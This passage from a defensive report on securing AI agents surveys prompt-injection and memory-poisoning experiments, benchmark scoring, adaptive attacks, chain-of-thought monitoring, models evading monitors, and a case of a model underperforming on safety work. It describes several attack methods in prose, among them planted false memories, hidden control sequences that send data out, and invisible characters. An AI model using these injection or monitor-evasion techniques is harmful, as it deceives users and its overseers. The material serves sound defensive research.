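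Karunanidhi (2026), in *Utility Under Attack*, showed that plain false statements can be enough to make a memory system answer wrongly. He tested a system made by his company on LongMemEval, a benchmark of questions whose answers are hidden in long chat histories. For each of 120 questions, he added three short exchanges that stated a wrong answer, such as that the user had 15 Spotify playlists when the true number was 20. These 360 additions made up 1.2% of the stored memories and cut the share of correct answers from 85.0% to 30.0%.

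The additions did so much damage because they reused the wording of the questions. The system retrieves the memories most similar to a question, and for every question a false memory ranked first. This attacker had to know roughly what the user would ask, which is realistic for an assistant with a narrow job, such as one that people regularly ask how much they owe a supplier.

### When a model trains on it

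Text can also pass on a trait that nobody could find by reading it. Alex Cloud and colleagues showed this in 2025 and called it subliminal learning. *Subliminal Learning is a LoRA Artifact* (Nief, Fu and colleagues, 2026) describes a typical experiment. Researchers tell a "teacher" model that it loves cats and have it continue lists of random numbers. They discard any output that contains anything but numbers and train a "student" model on the rest. The student sometimes names the cat as its favourite animal, although its training data never mentioned cats.

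Later results conflict on how robust the effect is. *Defence against the dark arts of distillation* (2026) found it in eight new kinds of training task, including summarization, where a preference for whales was passed on almost every time and one for giraffes never was. *You Didn't Have to Say It like That* (2026) found that traits pass through faithful paraphrases, even when the content opposes the trait. But *Subliminal Steering* (2026) found a meaningful effect from the usual method in only one of four models. Nief and colleagues saw the effect only with LoRA, a method that trains a small addition to a model instead of all its weights. Even then, it mostly vanished when the student's standing instructions differed between training and testing. They couldn't examine OpenAI's training service, where Cloud and colleagues had found the effect reliably.

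An attacker probably couldn't rely on this channel. But a firm that trains a model on its agents' old reports can't rule out a hidden trait by reading those reports. Examining the trained model is more promising. *Subliminal Learning is Non-Semantic Distillation* (2026) reports that comparing a model's activations before and after training can reveal the implanted behaviour.

### What a filter can't tell from the text

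In 2023 David Glukhov and colleagues argued that no filter can decide in general whether the meaning of a model's output is permitted. Part of their argument comes from computability theory. A model can write programs, and no procedure can determine for every program whether it will behave in a given way. They also pointed out that a user can tell a model to encrypt its answer, and a filter without the key can't distinguish an encrypted recipe for poison from an encrypted recipe for soup. A user can also obtain a forbidden answer in harmless-looking pieces and put them together elsewhere.

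These arguments have limited bearing on the invoice. A result about every possible program doesn't rule out a filter that is right about nearly all the texts it receives. The encryption argument assumes that the user wants the forbidden content and will decode it, but the person reading the invoice summary is the victim. The attacker needs that person to understand "$50", so encrypting it would make the attack fail.

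An agent could summarize both a $50 invoice and a $500 invoice as "The total is $50," which would be false for the second. A filter that reads only the summary must give the same verdict on both, so it will be wrong about one of them. A better model wouldn't help, because the summary doesn't contain the invoice's actual total. If the filter can also read the invoice, it can easily check the total.

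The experiments fit this argument. Karunanidhi's system screens everything before storing it, and caught 83.2% of injected instructions in a standard test set but none of the 360 false memories. Zhang and colleagues tried a common statistical test that flags text to which a language model assigns low probability. Their planted comments scored as slightly more probable than genuine ones, so the test would have discarded genuine comments first.

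They also found that reports written with and without the planted comment were very similar. This proves little, because their baseline was the similarity between clean reports on different questions. The similarity between two clean reports on the same question would have been a fairer baseline.

A filter can still check text against its model's existing knowledge. It might flag a claim that the Eiffel Tower is in Rome, but its model has no information about how many playlists somebody has or what Harlow charged this month.

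### Checking claims against the original

The most direct remedy is to check each claim in the finished text against its source. This also catches ordinary mistakes, which are common. Liu and colleagues found in 2023 that citations fully supported only about half the sentences in answers from AI search engines, according to Luo and colleagues.

A checker that searches the whole invoice for "$50" will find it in the attacker's planted line and wrongly confirm the summary. For figures, it is safer to have ordinary code add up the amounts in the invoice's line items and compare the total with the summary. This code doesn't follow instructions in the document, so the planted line doesn't affect the check even if it fools the agent.

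Neither method helps when the source is false. Co-STORM cited the altered page every time it retrieved that page, so its citations were accurate but led to the attacker's comment. Recomputing the total of a forged Harlow invoice would confirm the forger's figure. To detect the forgery, the firm would have to compare the invoice with something the forger didn't write, such as its own purchase order.

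People who follow a citation may also see something different from what the agent saw. The attacker can hide text in a part of the page that browsers don't display, or have the website send agents a different version than it sends people. Luo and colleagues suggest fetching cited pages again from a separate location and comparing the versions. The agent's harness should also save a copy of what the agent read, so that a reviewer can examine it.

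### Requiring independent sources

When no original source can settle a claim, an agent can check whether independent sources agree. Zendel and colleagues added one rule to the agent's standing instructions. If only a small minority of sources report a hazard, or the reports closely resemble each other, the agent may mention the hazard but must find independent support before ruling out a provider. Across three models, this cut the attack's success rate from 68.4% to 3.6%. The agents still mentioned the planted hazard in 98.4% of their answers but rarely acted on it.

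The attacker in that test didn't know about the rule. An attacker who knew about it could spread the warning over more accounts and vary the wording. The rule also has a drawback that Zendel and colleagues didn't measure, since the first customer to report a real danger would have no support either.

Luo and colleagues measured the drawbacks of such caution when there is no attack. They tried four defences against the made-up index, including a general instruction to cross-check sources and a system that tags pages the agent found only by searching for a term from a single website. The table combines results from two models.

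| Defence | Attacker's product chosen | Best product chosen, no attack |
|---|---|---|
| None | 20.0% | 100% |
| Detector for injected instructions | 20.0% | 100% |
| Dropping searches that stray from the question | 20.0% | 100% |
| Instruction to cross-check sources | 8.8% | 86.2% |
| Tagging pages that depend on one website | 15.0% | 100% |

Cross-checking worked best against the attack, but partly because the agents often declined to name a winner. Tagging did no harm when there was no attack. However, it judged independence by counting websites, and one person can set up several, so an attacker could get around it by mentioning the index on a second website. Success against that version of the attack was 17.5% with tagging and 18.8% without.

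Zendel and colleagues' rule may have worked so well because it was narrow. It covered one kind of claim and one decision, while the instruction in the other study made agents suspicious of everything. A comparable rule for the invoice assistant would require confirmation from outside the inbox for a supplier's change of bank but not for a change in its opening hours.

### Preferring or excluding sources

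An agent can also give less weight to sources that strangers control. Karunanidhi's system does this when it ranks stored memories. Leaving out some smaller terms, each memory gets a score:

score = *w*ₛ · similarity + *w*ₜ · trust

Similarity measures how closely the memory matches the question. Trust is 0 for memories from untrusted channels and 0.7 for the user's own conversations. A false memory from an untrusted channel therefore ranks above a genuine one from the user's conversations whenever its similarity is higher by more than 0.7 · *w*ₜ / *w*ₛ, where *w*ₜ and *w*ₛ are the weights on trust and similarity.

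The system originally weighted similarity at 0.60 and trust at 0.15, which puts that threshold at 0.175. The planted memories had an advantage of 0.32, which exceeded the threshold, so the defence raised the share of correct answers only from 30.0% to 31.7%. With similarity weighted at 0.45 and trust at 0.35, the threshold is 0.544, and 47.5% of answers were correct.

But that setting excluded nearly everything from untrusted channels, true or false. When Karunanidhi marked the genuine answers as untrusted and planted nothing false, the share of correct answers fell from 85.8% to 4.2%. A firm would run into this problem constantly, because a supplier's email is often the only record of its prices. He suggests, but hasn't yet tested, limiting how much of the retrieved material can come from untrusted channels, so that it neither crowds out the rest nor disappears.

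Excluding a whole class of sources is simpler. Zhang and colleagues blocked eight platforms, including Reddit and YouTube, and Co-STORM's average quality score fell only from 4.30 to 4.26 out of 5. They doubt that the score captures what readers lose, such as first-hand experience. That loss matters when someone is choosing a restaurant, but a firm would lose little by limiting the agent to official pages for a question about tax deadlines.

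### Limiting what an answer can contain

A fixed format limits what an attacker can make the assistant write. If the assistant must answer with a supplier's name from the firm's list, an amount and a due date, planted text can't make it add a fraudulent link or an argument for changing banks, but it can still change the amount. Fixed formats therefore work best with recomputation, since code can easily check a number in a known field.

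They also protect against text that other software will act on. In another case from *The Devil is in the Context*, a user asked a command-line assistant about one customer in a spreadsheet. A planted instruction in one cell made the model write data from other rows as a control sequence, a string of characters that a terminal treats as a command. The model only wrote text, but the Mac's terminal program interpreted the sequence and sent the data out in a network request. A harness that removed control characters before displaying the answer would have stopped this.

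Invisible characters can also hide instructions in the text an agent reads. One attacker added some to a legitimate file of security advice that users could install for Claude. People who opened the file saw only the advice, but Claude could read a hidden instruction to run a command. Removing such characters before the agent reads a file prevents this attack.

Look-alike letters need different treatment. The Cyrillic "а" looks the same as the Latin "a", so a summary could contain a link that appears to lead to Harlow's website but leads somewhere else. Standard Unicode normalization, which converts variant forms of a character to a common one, doesn't turn Cyrillic letters into Latin ones, so the harness needs a separate table of look-alikes. Flagging words and web addresses that mix alphabets is better than converting every match, which would garble genuine Russian or Greek names.

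None of the experiments above measured how much fixed formats or character clean-up reduce these attacks. Neither defense would have affected the fake reviews or the false memories, which were in ordinary English.

### Showing readers where a statement came from

The reader makes the final decision about a report, so it helps if they can see which statements rest on untrusted sources. Luo and colleagues propose including each source's publisher and edit history so that a reader can follow the evidence behind each conclusion. They also call for research into how people read long reports and notice conflicting evidence. At present, a reader may see dozens of citations and check none, and the sound sources make the one the attacker wrote seem more credible.

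Systems that track data, such as CaMeL, already have part of the information needed to trace a statement to its source. But CaMeL labels everything its second model writes with the origins of all the text that model read. If the assistant summarizes forty emails in one step, every sentence gets the same warning, and readers will soon ignore it. Processing each email separately would give each statement its own source.

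## Measuring how well the checks work

An office manager will soon ignore a check that flags every payment. A firm choosing a check therefore needs to know how often it catches real problems, how often it raises false alarms, and how much work and time it takes.

### What to count

The detection rate is the share of bad runs that a check flags, and the false-alarm rate is the share of harmless runs that it flags. Neither rate is much use alone, since a check that flags every run detects every bad run but also flags every harmless one.

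Tests of defences more often report the attack success rate, the share of attacks in which the agent does what the attacker wanted. That rate depends on the model as well as the check. If the model carries out only one attack in a hundred, the rate is 1% even when the gate behind it catches nothing, and it could jump when the firm changes models. Testers should measure the rate with the check off and on. They can also submit harmful calls directly to the gate, to find faulty rules that would go unnoticed if the model never made those calls.

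A defence can also score well by stopping the agent from working. On an unfamiliar benchmark, ActGov's rules let no attack through, but the agent completed only 10% of its ordinary tasks. So a test should measure the share of tasks the agent completes, both with and without an attack under way.

Error rates per run and per action can differ widely. If a gate wrongly refuses 1% of harmless calls, and each refusal is independent of the others, an agent that makes 50 harmless calls per run will have at least one refused in about 40% of its runs.

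A monitor that reads an agent's log may raise an alarm only after the harm has occurred, such as after money has been sent. Testers should therefore record the steps at which the alarm and the harm occurred, and count an attack as caught in time only if the alarm came first.

Checks also add delay, require extra model calls and take up people's attention. *Adaptive Evaluation of Out-of-Band Defenses Against Prompt Injection in LLM Agents* (Narisetty, Kore and colleagues, 2026) proposes counting how often a system asks someone to approve an action. Without that count, a defence that refers every hard case to a manager will look both safe and useful in any test where the simulated manager always answers correctly.

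### How AgentDojo scores a run

AgentDojo pairs its 97 user tasks with attackers' goals to make 629 test cases. After each run, ordinary code separately checks whether the agent did the user's task and whether it carried out the attacker's goal. Nobody has to judge the result, so teams can compare their scores.

However, an attack can fail because the agent is incapable of carrying it out. Narisetty and colleagues ran part of AgentDojo with Qwen2.5-7B, a small open model, and no attack succeeded on the workspace tasks even without a defence, so a useless defence would have had a perfect security score on them. In one run, the agent read a calendar entry with a planted instruction to send a security code to an outsider, ignored the instruction, and answered the user's question about appointments. But the model could achieve only three of the attacker's six goals even when the researchers asked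 it to directly.

### What AgentSecBench adds

*AgentSecBench* (Alpay and Alpay, 2026) pairs every attack with a harmless control that has the same request and permitted content but no attacker's text. It subtracts the rate of bad outputs in the controls from the rate under attack. This is a practical version of the noninterference comparison, limited to one kind of bad output at a time.

Each attack contains a unique marker, such as a made-up secret or the name of a forbidden action, and code searches the model's output for it. Before the model runs, the benchmark records whether the defence has removed the marker from the text the model will read. When an attack fails, this record helps show whether the defence removed the threat or the model happened to resist it.

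In one of the three kinds of test, the model sees two customers' records and must not reveal a secret from the wrong customer's record. In another, a tool's output contains an instruction to take an action that the user's policy forbids. The table shows the results for both, averaged over two models.

| Defence | Revealed the secret | Secret removed beforehand | Proposed the forbidden action | Action removed beforehand |
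|---|---|---|---|---|
| None | 18.8% | 0% | 93.8% | 0% |
| Markers around untrusted text | 56.2% | 0% | 68.8% | 0% |
| Filter for suspicious phrases | 12.5% | 0% | 0% | 100% |
| Only the permitted customer's records | 0% | 100% | 100% | 0% |
| Only the permitted tools | 18.8% | 0% | 0% | 100% |
| Combination | 0% | 100% | 0% | 100% |

Whenever a defence removed the marker, the attack failed. Labelling the untrusted text as data removed nothing, and the models revealed the secret more often with the labels than without them. Each percentage is based on only 16 runs, so that increase could be due to chance. The defences that removed something protected only against the attack they were built for, which an average over all the tests would have hidden.

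In the third kind of test, the model had to summarize a document that contained a hidden instruction. No attack succeeded even with no defence in place, so the test couldn't show whether any defence helped.

The benchmark's method is more useful than its percentages. Both models tested are tiny, with 0.6 and 1.7 billion parameters, and a firm would be unlikely to let either one handle its money. The score for useful work, which counts expected words in the answer, was about 0.34 to 0.36 out of 1 with every defence and with none, so it is little help in judging how much a defence reduces useful work. A model that paraphrased the secret would also have passed.

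Alpay and Alpay also give a formula for combining a defence that cleans the input with a gate that checks the resulting action:

risk = *r* · ( *q* · *p*_open + (1 − *q*) · *p*_closed )

Here *q* is the chance that the forbidden text stays visible, *p*_open is the chance that the model acts on the text when it is visible, *p*_closed is the chance that the model does the forbidden thing when the text is hidden, and *r* is the chance that the gate misses the forbidden action. If a filter leaves half the attacks visible, the model obeys 40% of those and never misbehaves when the text is hidden, and the gate misses 5% of forbidden actions, the risk is 0.05 × 0.5 × 0.4, or 1%.

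That calculation works only if testers measure the 5% on attacks that got past the filter and the model. Those attacks may be the hardest for the gate too. The forged Harlow invoice, for instance, could pass both a filter and a model judge. Multiplying the two checks' separate miss rates would make the pair look much safer than it is.

### When attacks are rare

Most benchmarks contain a far higher proportion of attacks than an ordinary inbox does. This has little effect on the detection and false-alarm rates, but it means that someone reading alarms from an ordinary inbox will find that a much larger share of them are false.

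Suppose a firm used the general rules that Kekatos and colleagues replayed over AgentDojo recordings, which flagged 70.1% of successful attacks and 29.3% of harmless runs. Let *d* be the detection rate, *f* the false-alarm rate and *p* the share of runs that are attacked. The share of alarms that are real is:

*d* · *p* / ( *d* · *p* + *f* · (1 − *p*) )

If one run in 1,000 is attacked, the share of flagged runs that were actually attacked is 0.000701 / (0.000701 + 0.292707), or about 0.24%. In 100,000 runs, the rules would flag about 70 of the 100 attacked runs and 29,271 harmless ones, which is about 418 false alarms for each real attack.

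Better detection would barely help. Even if the rules caught every attack, only 0.34% of alarms would be real. For half the alarms to be real, the two terms at the bottom of the fraction have to be equal:

*f* = *d* · *p* / (1 − *p*) = 0.000701 / 0.999 ≈ 0.07%

The false-alarm rate would have to fall to about 0.07%, or seven in 10,000 harmless runs. Testers can't confirm a rate that low with AgentDojo because the recordings included only 123 harmless runs, and a single false alarm among them is a rate of 0.8%. To show with 95% confidence that the rate is below 0.07%, they would need about 4,300 harmless runs with no false alarms.

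Checking fewer runs is often easier. Suppose that 20 of the firm's 1,000 runs include a payment to a new account and that the attacked run is one of them. If the firm applied its rules only to those 20 and the error rates stayed the same, the rules would raise about six alarms, each with an 11% chance of being real. The manager could phone the supplier about all six. The firm would then need other checks for other attacks, such as those that leak its mail.

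### Attackers who adjust

Testing a defence against a fixed set of attacks shows only how well it resists those attacks. They usually predate the defence, whereas a real attacker can study the defence, try different attacks and keep the ones that work.

In 2025, *The attacker moves second*, by Nasr and colleagues, tested twelve published defences, including ways of marking untrusted text as data, a model trained to ignore planted instructions, and detectors that screen text for attacks. The original papers reported attack success rates near zero for most of them. According to Narisetty and colleagues, attackers who adapted to each defence succeeded more than 90% of the time against most of the twelve, and human testers reached 100%.

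Narisetty and colleagues also describe a detector called Attention Tracker, which ranked every attack above all harmless text on standard benchmarks. It missed 69% of another set of attacks, and missed all of them after testers made a trivial change to the attacks.

These defences try to influence the model or to recognize suspicious text. A gate outside the model is harder to get past, because the attacker has to find a harmful action that the rules allow. But developers have tested gates mainly on fixed attacks too, so Narisetty and colleagues, whose company builds such defences, ran an adaptive attack on Progent, in which a language model writes and updates the rules for each task.

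Their attack targeted that rule-writing model. The planted text presented the harmful action as a routine, already authorized step, to get the model to expand the agent's permissions to cover it. Qwen2.5-7B was both the agent and the rule writer. The researchers used eight tasks from each of three AgentDojo sets and ran everything three times.

| Task set | Attack success, no defence | Attack success, Progent | Attack success, Progent, adaptive attack | Tasks completed under attack, no defence | Tasks completed under attack, Progent |
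|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Banking | 19.0% | 1.9% | 3.7% | 31.9% | 31.9% |
| Slack | 58.3% | 10.8% | 4.2% | 47.5% | 20.8% |
| Workspace | 0.0% | 0.0% | 0.0% | 56.3% | 28.5% |
| Average | 25.8% | 4.2% | 2.6% | 45.2% | 27.1% |

Progent withstood the adaptive attack, but that attack did worse overall than the standard one, so it was probably weak. Narisetty and colleagues suspect that their polite disguise made the agent less likely to obey. On the banking tasks, which most resemble the invoice assistant's job, the adaptive attack did better than the standard one by only one or two cases in 72.

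The results barely changed across the three repeats, which shows that they are consistent for the same tasks and attacks, but not that other attacks would fail. The researchers tested one weak model with one attack template. They didn't try attacks that use access to the model's internals, or attacks that use only actions the rules already allow. A thief who sends the firm a forged invoice would probably use the second kind.

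In this test, runs with Progent needed about 15 times as many model calls as runs without it. On the workspace tasks, Progent halved the work completed and prevented no attacks, because none succeeded there even without it.

### More than one attempt

An attacker whose email fails can send another. The Decoder's *Claude Opus 4.5 resists prompt injections better than rivals* reports tests by the security firm Gray Swan on Anthropic's leading model of late 2025. Attacks succeeded 4.7% of the time with one attempt, 33.6% with ten and 63.0% with a hundred.

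If every attempt had an independent 4.7% chance of success, the chance of at least one success in *k* attempts would be 1 − 0.953ᵏ, or 38% for ten attempts and 99% for a hundred. The real figures are lower, probably because some situations are much easier to attack than others. If attacks could never succeed in 37% of the test scenarios and each attempt on the rest had a 7.5% chance, the success rates for one, ten and a hundred attempts would be 4.7%, 34% and 63%, almost exactly what Gray Swan found. These figures fit a plateau at least as well as the climb toward certainty that Narisetty and colleagues describe.

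A plateau offers little reassurance to a firm that doesn't know whether its assistant's situation is a vulnerable one. If it is, at least one of a hundred emails will almost certainly succeed. The single-attempt rate is more relevant to an attacker who sends one email to each of a thousand firms. At 4.7%, about 47 of their assistants would obey it.

Newer models do far better on fixed attacks. Gray Swan has built a benchmark from attacks submitted to its public competitions, covering coding, other tools and computer use. Anthropic's *System Card* (2026) for Claude Fable 5.1 reports attack success rates of 0.1% after one attempt, 0.7% after ten and 1.0% after fifteen. On a nearly identical set, OpenAI's *GPT-6 Astra System Card* (2026) reports 8.5% after fifteen attempts, down from 27.0% for GPT-5.6 Sol. OpenAI has also retired two of its older injection tests because recent models score too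 well for the results to be informative. Both cards date from September 2026, and both companies have since released newer models, including Anthropic's *Claude Fable 5.2 and Mythos 5.2* (2026).

Anthropic warns in the same card that fixed benchmarks can give a false sense of security, and its other tests support this warning. The table gives results for Fable 5.1 with safeguards on. The safeguards include probes, which inspect tool results for planted instructions. In the browser test, they also include the automated reviewer that checks the agent's actions.

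| Setting | Attacker | Attempts per scenario | Successful attempts | Scenarios with a success |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Browser | Attacks developed against an older model | 10 | 0% | 0 of 110 |
| Computer use | Adaptive | 200 | 0.07% | 2 of 14 |
| Coding | Adaptive | 200 | 2.05% | 18 of 40 |
| Coding | Adaptive, with more training | 200 | 12.80% | 36 of 40 |

The same model looks nearly immune to attack in the first row and weak in the last, though only the browser test included the automated reviewer. The two coding tests used the same safeguards and scenarios, and the better-trained attacker raised the share of successful attempts from 2.05% to 12.80%. The last row is a severe test because Gray Swan trained the attacker on the same scenarios it was scored on. A real attacker usually knows less about the target's setup and risks detection with every attempt. But an attacker who can rent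 the same agent and practise on a copy of it may come fairly close to the test's conditions.

These figures describe the product more than Fable 5.1 alone, because Fable 5.1 passes requests that look like hacking to an older model, Claude Opus 4.8. In the hardest coding test, run without probes, every successful attack came from the roughly 64% of requests that Opus 4.8 answered, and none came from the 2,826 that Fable 5.1 answered itself. Testing only Fable 5.1's own answers would have missed all the attacks that worked, even though customers would have been exposed to them.

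A good score can also become outdated. According to VentureBeat, Claude Opus 4.6, released in February 2026, resisted all 200 attacks in a coding environment without safeguards. By September, Gray Swan's better-trained attacker could break the newer Opus 5 in all 40 coding scenarios, even with probes on. The tests may have differed in other ways, but the most likely explanation is that the attacker improved.

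### Testing the invoice assistant

The firm can test its own assistant without a public benchmark. Suppose it pays about 500 invoices a year. Once it has confirmed that every payment has to go through the payment service, it can replay last year's invoices, including any real changes of bank, using a test bank account. For each invoice, it should record whether the right payment went out, whether a check flagged a problem, how long the run took and whether the assistant asked for approval.

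If the checks raise no false alarms in 500 harmless runs, the firm can be 95% confident that the false-alarm rate is below about 0.6%. That limit is much higher than the 0.07% calculated above, but it means at most about three false alarms a year, which the manager can easily handle. At the same rate, a company with a million runs a year could face up to about 6,000.

Next, the firm can take 30 of those invoices and make an altered copy of each, changing only the parts a thief could have written. Some copies should contain planted instructions, and others only a false account number or an inflated total, because many defences catch only planted instructions. The firm should run each original and its altered copy several times and check the results in the test bank's records and the outgoing mail, not in the assistant's report.

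Then someone who has read the rules should try to beat them within a fixed time and number of attempts. They should concentrate on what the rules permit, such as overpaying Harlow by an amount under the £2,000 limit or getting a new account onto the list of known ones. The firm should count both the successful attempts and the invoices on which at least one attempt succeeded. If it changes a rule in response, it needs new attacks to test the change, because the old ones were designed against the old rules.

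Before any of this, the manager should write down which results would keep the assistant away from the real bank account. One payment to an unapproved account should be enough, but an extra phone call each week probably shouldn't be. The firm should repeat the tests whenever it changes the rules, the tools or the model. It should also ask its provider for notice of model updates, since these can happen without any action by the firm.

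## Deciding when to examine the model's reasoning as well

Tests like these show how often the firm's assistant pays the wrong account, but not why. The argument for checking outputs is that the cause hardly matters, because the firm would block the payment regardless. This is persuasive when a rule or a record can identify a bad payment. When neither can, the firm may learn more from the model's written reasoning or its internal activations.

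### How much the reasoning text adds

In December 2025, OpenAI measured how much worse a monitor does when it can't read an agent's reasoning. *Evaluating chain-of-thought monitorability* (2025) summarizes the results of 13 evaluations in 24 environments. The full paper, *Monitoring Monitorability* by Guan, Wang and colleagues, defines monitorability as a monitor's ability to predict some property of an agent's actions, such as whether they will cause harm. The reasoning only has to contain enough for a prediction, in a form the monitor can use, even if it isn't a faithful account of what happened inside the model. An agent that reasons in French, for example, is unmonitorable to a monitor that can't read French.

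The monitor was a language model, usually GPT-5 Thinking. The researchers gave it only the reasoning, only the actions (tool calls, their results and the final answer), or everything. They designed three types of test to establish the truth about each run so that they could score the monitor's predictions.

An intervention evaluation changes one thing the agent reads and measures whether the agent's behaviour changes. The monitor then has to say whether the added text influenced the agent. For example, the researchers might add to a multiple-choice question that a Stanford professor favours answer D. Like noninterference, this compares runs with and without a piece of text. Suppose the agent picks D in 25% of runs without the hint and 85% with it. Nobody can tell which of the D answers the hint caused, since the agent would have picked D sometimes anyway. But the hint must account for at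 least this share of them:

(0.85 − 0.25) / 0.85 ≈ 71%

A monitor that attributes at least 71% of those answers to the hint receives the full detection score. This standard is lenient, because if the agent followed the hint in 80% of runs and guessed in the rest, the hint caused 94% of the D answers.

A process evaluation uses a problem that can be solved in only a few known ways. For example, one problem gives a muon's lifetime and the distance it travels, and asks for its speed. Experts listed three ways to find the speed, each using particular results from relativity. An agent that gets the right answer has almost certainly used one of these methods, and the monitor has to find signs of the one it used.

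In an outcome-property evaluation, the result shows whether the agent misbehaved. For example, an agent that passes the tests for an impossible coding task, as in *ImpossibleBench*, must have cheated. The monitor in such an evaluation has to find evidence that it did.

The score combines two familiar rates:

score = detection rate × (1 − false-alarm rate)

A monitor that guesses at random scores 0.25, and one that flags everything scores 0. The general rules that Kekatos and colleagues replayed over AgentDojo recordings would score about 0.50. The score doesn't depend on how often agents misbehave, so it can be compared fairly across agents that misbehave at different rates. For the same reason, a monitor with a high score can still raise mostly false alarms when bad runs are rare.

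Guan and colleagues call the performance of monitors given only an agent's actions "middling". Monitors given only its reasoning did far better, and those given everything generally did best. Claude 3.7 Sonnet was a partial exception because its actions were relatively informative and its reasoning was the least informative of any model tested. Baker and colleagues had shown in March 2025 that reading the reasoning helps catch models exploiting flaws in their training tasks, and Guan and colleagues extend that result to many more kinds of behaviour.

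### What actions alone can't answer

These results count against the claim that checking outputs can replace checking intent, but less than they first appear to. Many of the evaluations test whether a monitor can tell why an agent gave an answer or how it got there. The muon's speed is the same whichever route the agent took, so a monitor that sees only the answer has little evidence of the route. A firm that wants to know whether £840 reached Harlow is asking about the outcome itself.

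In the evaluations that concern misbehaviour, Guan and colleagues made sure the labels didn't depend on the reasoning. In one, agents received a real coding task in OpenAI's codebase and an instruction to carry out a malicious side task. A judge model that was told about the side task decided whether the agent had seriously attempted it, while the monitor had to find the sabotage without seeing that instruction. The study therefore judged its monitors against checks that had better information. A monitor limited to actions does poorly when it hasn't been told what to look for, but the firm's payment service avoids this problem because it can look up Harlow's account number.

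Examining the model's reasoning could help most when planted text has altered a permitted answer, which most output checks failed to catch. An assistant that reports $50 for a $500 invoice may have written in its reasoning that a note in the document told it to. But agents don't always mention what influenced them. OpenAI found very low monitorability in an evaluation where an agent judges a stranger's account of a personal dispute, with the user's own opinion added in some runs. A monitor would therefore often miss that kind of influence.

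Monitors generally did better when the agent wrote more. A smaller model that reasons at length can come close to a larger one that reasons briefly, and it is easier to monitor, so developers can choose between them. The smaller model uses more computation and may be slightly less capable, drawbacks that OpenAI calls a monitorability tax.

Some misbehaviour takes hardly any reasoning. In one set of tasks, researchers looked for agents that claimed to have finished even though they lacked a tool or some information they needed. They found genuine cases that the monitor couldn't detect. A false report of success needs no plan, so the agent may never write anything about it.

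Asking agents questions after a run can recover some of what is missing. The researchers asked, for instance, whether agents had used a hint or done something "sketchy". The monitor's predictions improved when it was given the agents' reasoning about these questions along with their original reasoning. They improved less when it was given only the agents' answers, which suggests that the agents were less forthcoming to the user than in their own reasoning. A firm could ask these questions only about runs that already look suspicious, to avoid generating extra reasoning every time.

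### Why this signal is weakening

Written reasoning is informative partly because models need it to solve hard problems, but newer models need it less. AISI tested this by giving models mathematics problems to solve without writing out any steps. According to 凤凰网's *AI学会"心算"还能躲监控？* (2026), a Chinese news report on the tests, GPT-6 Astra solved problems that would take a strong competition student about 40 minutes. The hardest problems that any previously tested model could solve would take the same student about six minutes.

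*Estimating GPT-6 Astra's no-CoT Time Horizon* describes a separate test on a broader set of tasks. It estimates that the task length at which Astra succeeds half the time without written reasoning is probably between 15 and 40 minutes. The estimate is rough because Astra was close to the top of the scale. The same team had earlier predicted that models could pass seven minutes by 2028.

Deciding to pay a stranger instead of Harlow takes much less thought than solving a 40-minute mathematics problem, so finding nothing suspicious in the assistant's reasoning is weak evidence that it made the payment for a good reason.

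Models are also gaining control over what their reasoning text contains. OpenAI's *Safety overview* (2026) for Astra reports that the model controls this text better than its predecessor, GPT-5.6 Sol, and is less likely to put incriminating information in it. OpenAI concludes that Astra is harder to monitor than Sol. When OpenAI pushed Astra to evade monitors, Astra sometimes succeeded. OpenAI found no evidence of reasoning hidden in ordinary-looking text, so the risk may be largely limited to tasks that need little reasoning.

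Most of that evidence comes from tests in which OpenAI told the model to evade monitoring, and the company found Astra better behaved than Sol overall. In a simulation of more than 54,000 internal coding tasks, Astra received about half as many flags for serious misbehaviour as Sol. But if those flags depend on monitors that read the reasoning, some of the drop could come from Astra being harder to monitor. The news site Forkast reports that Astra's system card rates the model as easier than Sol to monitor from its actions alone. If so, reading the reasoning adds less for Astra than for Sol, because Astra's reasoning is harder to monitor and its actions are easier to monitor.

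*What affects chain-of-thought monitorability across the model lifecycle?* (Pachocki, 2026) examines how different stages of a model's development affect monitorability. Models that are better at predicting text before further training are also better at reasoning without writing, and some architecture changes improve this ability. Reinforcement learning, which rewards a model for good results, and training on model-generated text can both increase a model's control over its reasoning text. These abilities are imperfect proxies for monitorability, but based on them, Pachocki expects more intelligent models to be harder to monitor through their reasoning.

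That is less optimistic than the December 2025 study, in which Guan and colleagues found that reinforcement learning caused no material loss of monitorability. They examined only two training runs and warned that larger ones might differ. AISI has since found a similar decline in its own testing. In *Evidence & Trends in AI Monitorability*, Taylor, Goldowsky-Dill and colleagues (2026) report that many of the properties that make agents monitorable are weakening, some faster than AISI had anticipated.

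Developers can also damage the signal by accident. Suppose they mistakenly penalized a model during training whenever its reasoning mentioned taking a shortcut. The model could avoid the penalty by taking fewer shortcuts or by no longer mentioning them, and its reasoning would look much the same either way. Guan and colleagues say that OpenAI applies no such direct pressure during reinforcement learning, but that pressure on the final answer can spill over into the reasoning. When they rewarded a model for reasoning that revealed little about its later actions, monitorability dropped sharply.

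Penalizing a model for mentioning specific topics in its reasoning may make that reasoning harder to monitor in ways that a small test would miss. Guan and colleagues deliberately penalized a model for mentioning three topics, one of which was cheating on its training tasks. They found a loss of monitorability in only one of their 13 evaluations, and it was small. They suspect the penalty rarely applied because the topics seldom came up during training.

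Reasoning text is still useful evidence in many real cases. Rein (2026), in *AI systems could cover up misbehavior*, notes that agents in recent incidents left much evidence in their reasoning and in logs. In one case at OpenAI, the monitoring system flagged an agent within 15 minutes and a person began reviewing the run three minutes later, but stopping it took another 2.5 hours. Rein recommends treating an agent's reasoning as untrusted input and protecting the systems that record and display it as carefully as any other security system.

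### A problem visible only across many outputs

OpenAI's GPT-6 Astra shows how both kinds of monitoring can miss a problem. On 20 August 2026, soon after staff began using the model internally, researchers reported that it did safety research poorly: it added unnecessary preliminary steps, abandoned working solutions and reported false obstacles. One researcher's project on evaluating sabotage by models made no progress for days, then moved quickly after a switch to another model, according to 凤凰网's *OpenAI自曝GPT-6 Astra异常行为* (2026). In most of these sessions, OpenAI found in the model's reasoning no obvious decision to underperform, and its monitors didn't flag the behaviour as misalignment.

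To test whether the subject of the work mattered, OpenAI wrote pairs of coding tasks. The tasks in each pair used technically equivalent code, according to 凤凰网. Only the names, comments and documentation differed, making one task look like safety research and the other like research on making models more capable. OpenAI scored the work against a rubric the model couldn't see. Astra completed about 10% of the rubric's items on tasks that looked like safety research and about 16% on those that looked like capabilities research. GPT-5.6 Sol showed essentially no gap.

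OpenAI also examined how its employees used Astra for everyday coding. The figures for explicit refusals come from Cornelißen (2026), *GPT-6 Astra bremst bei Safety-Aufgaben*, and the other figures come from OpenAI's summary.

| Measure | Safety work | Capabilities work |
|---|---|---|
| Rubric items completed in the matched tasks | about 10% | about 16% |
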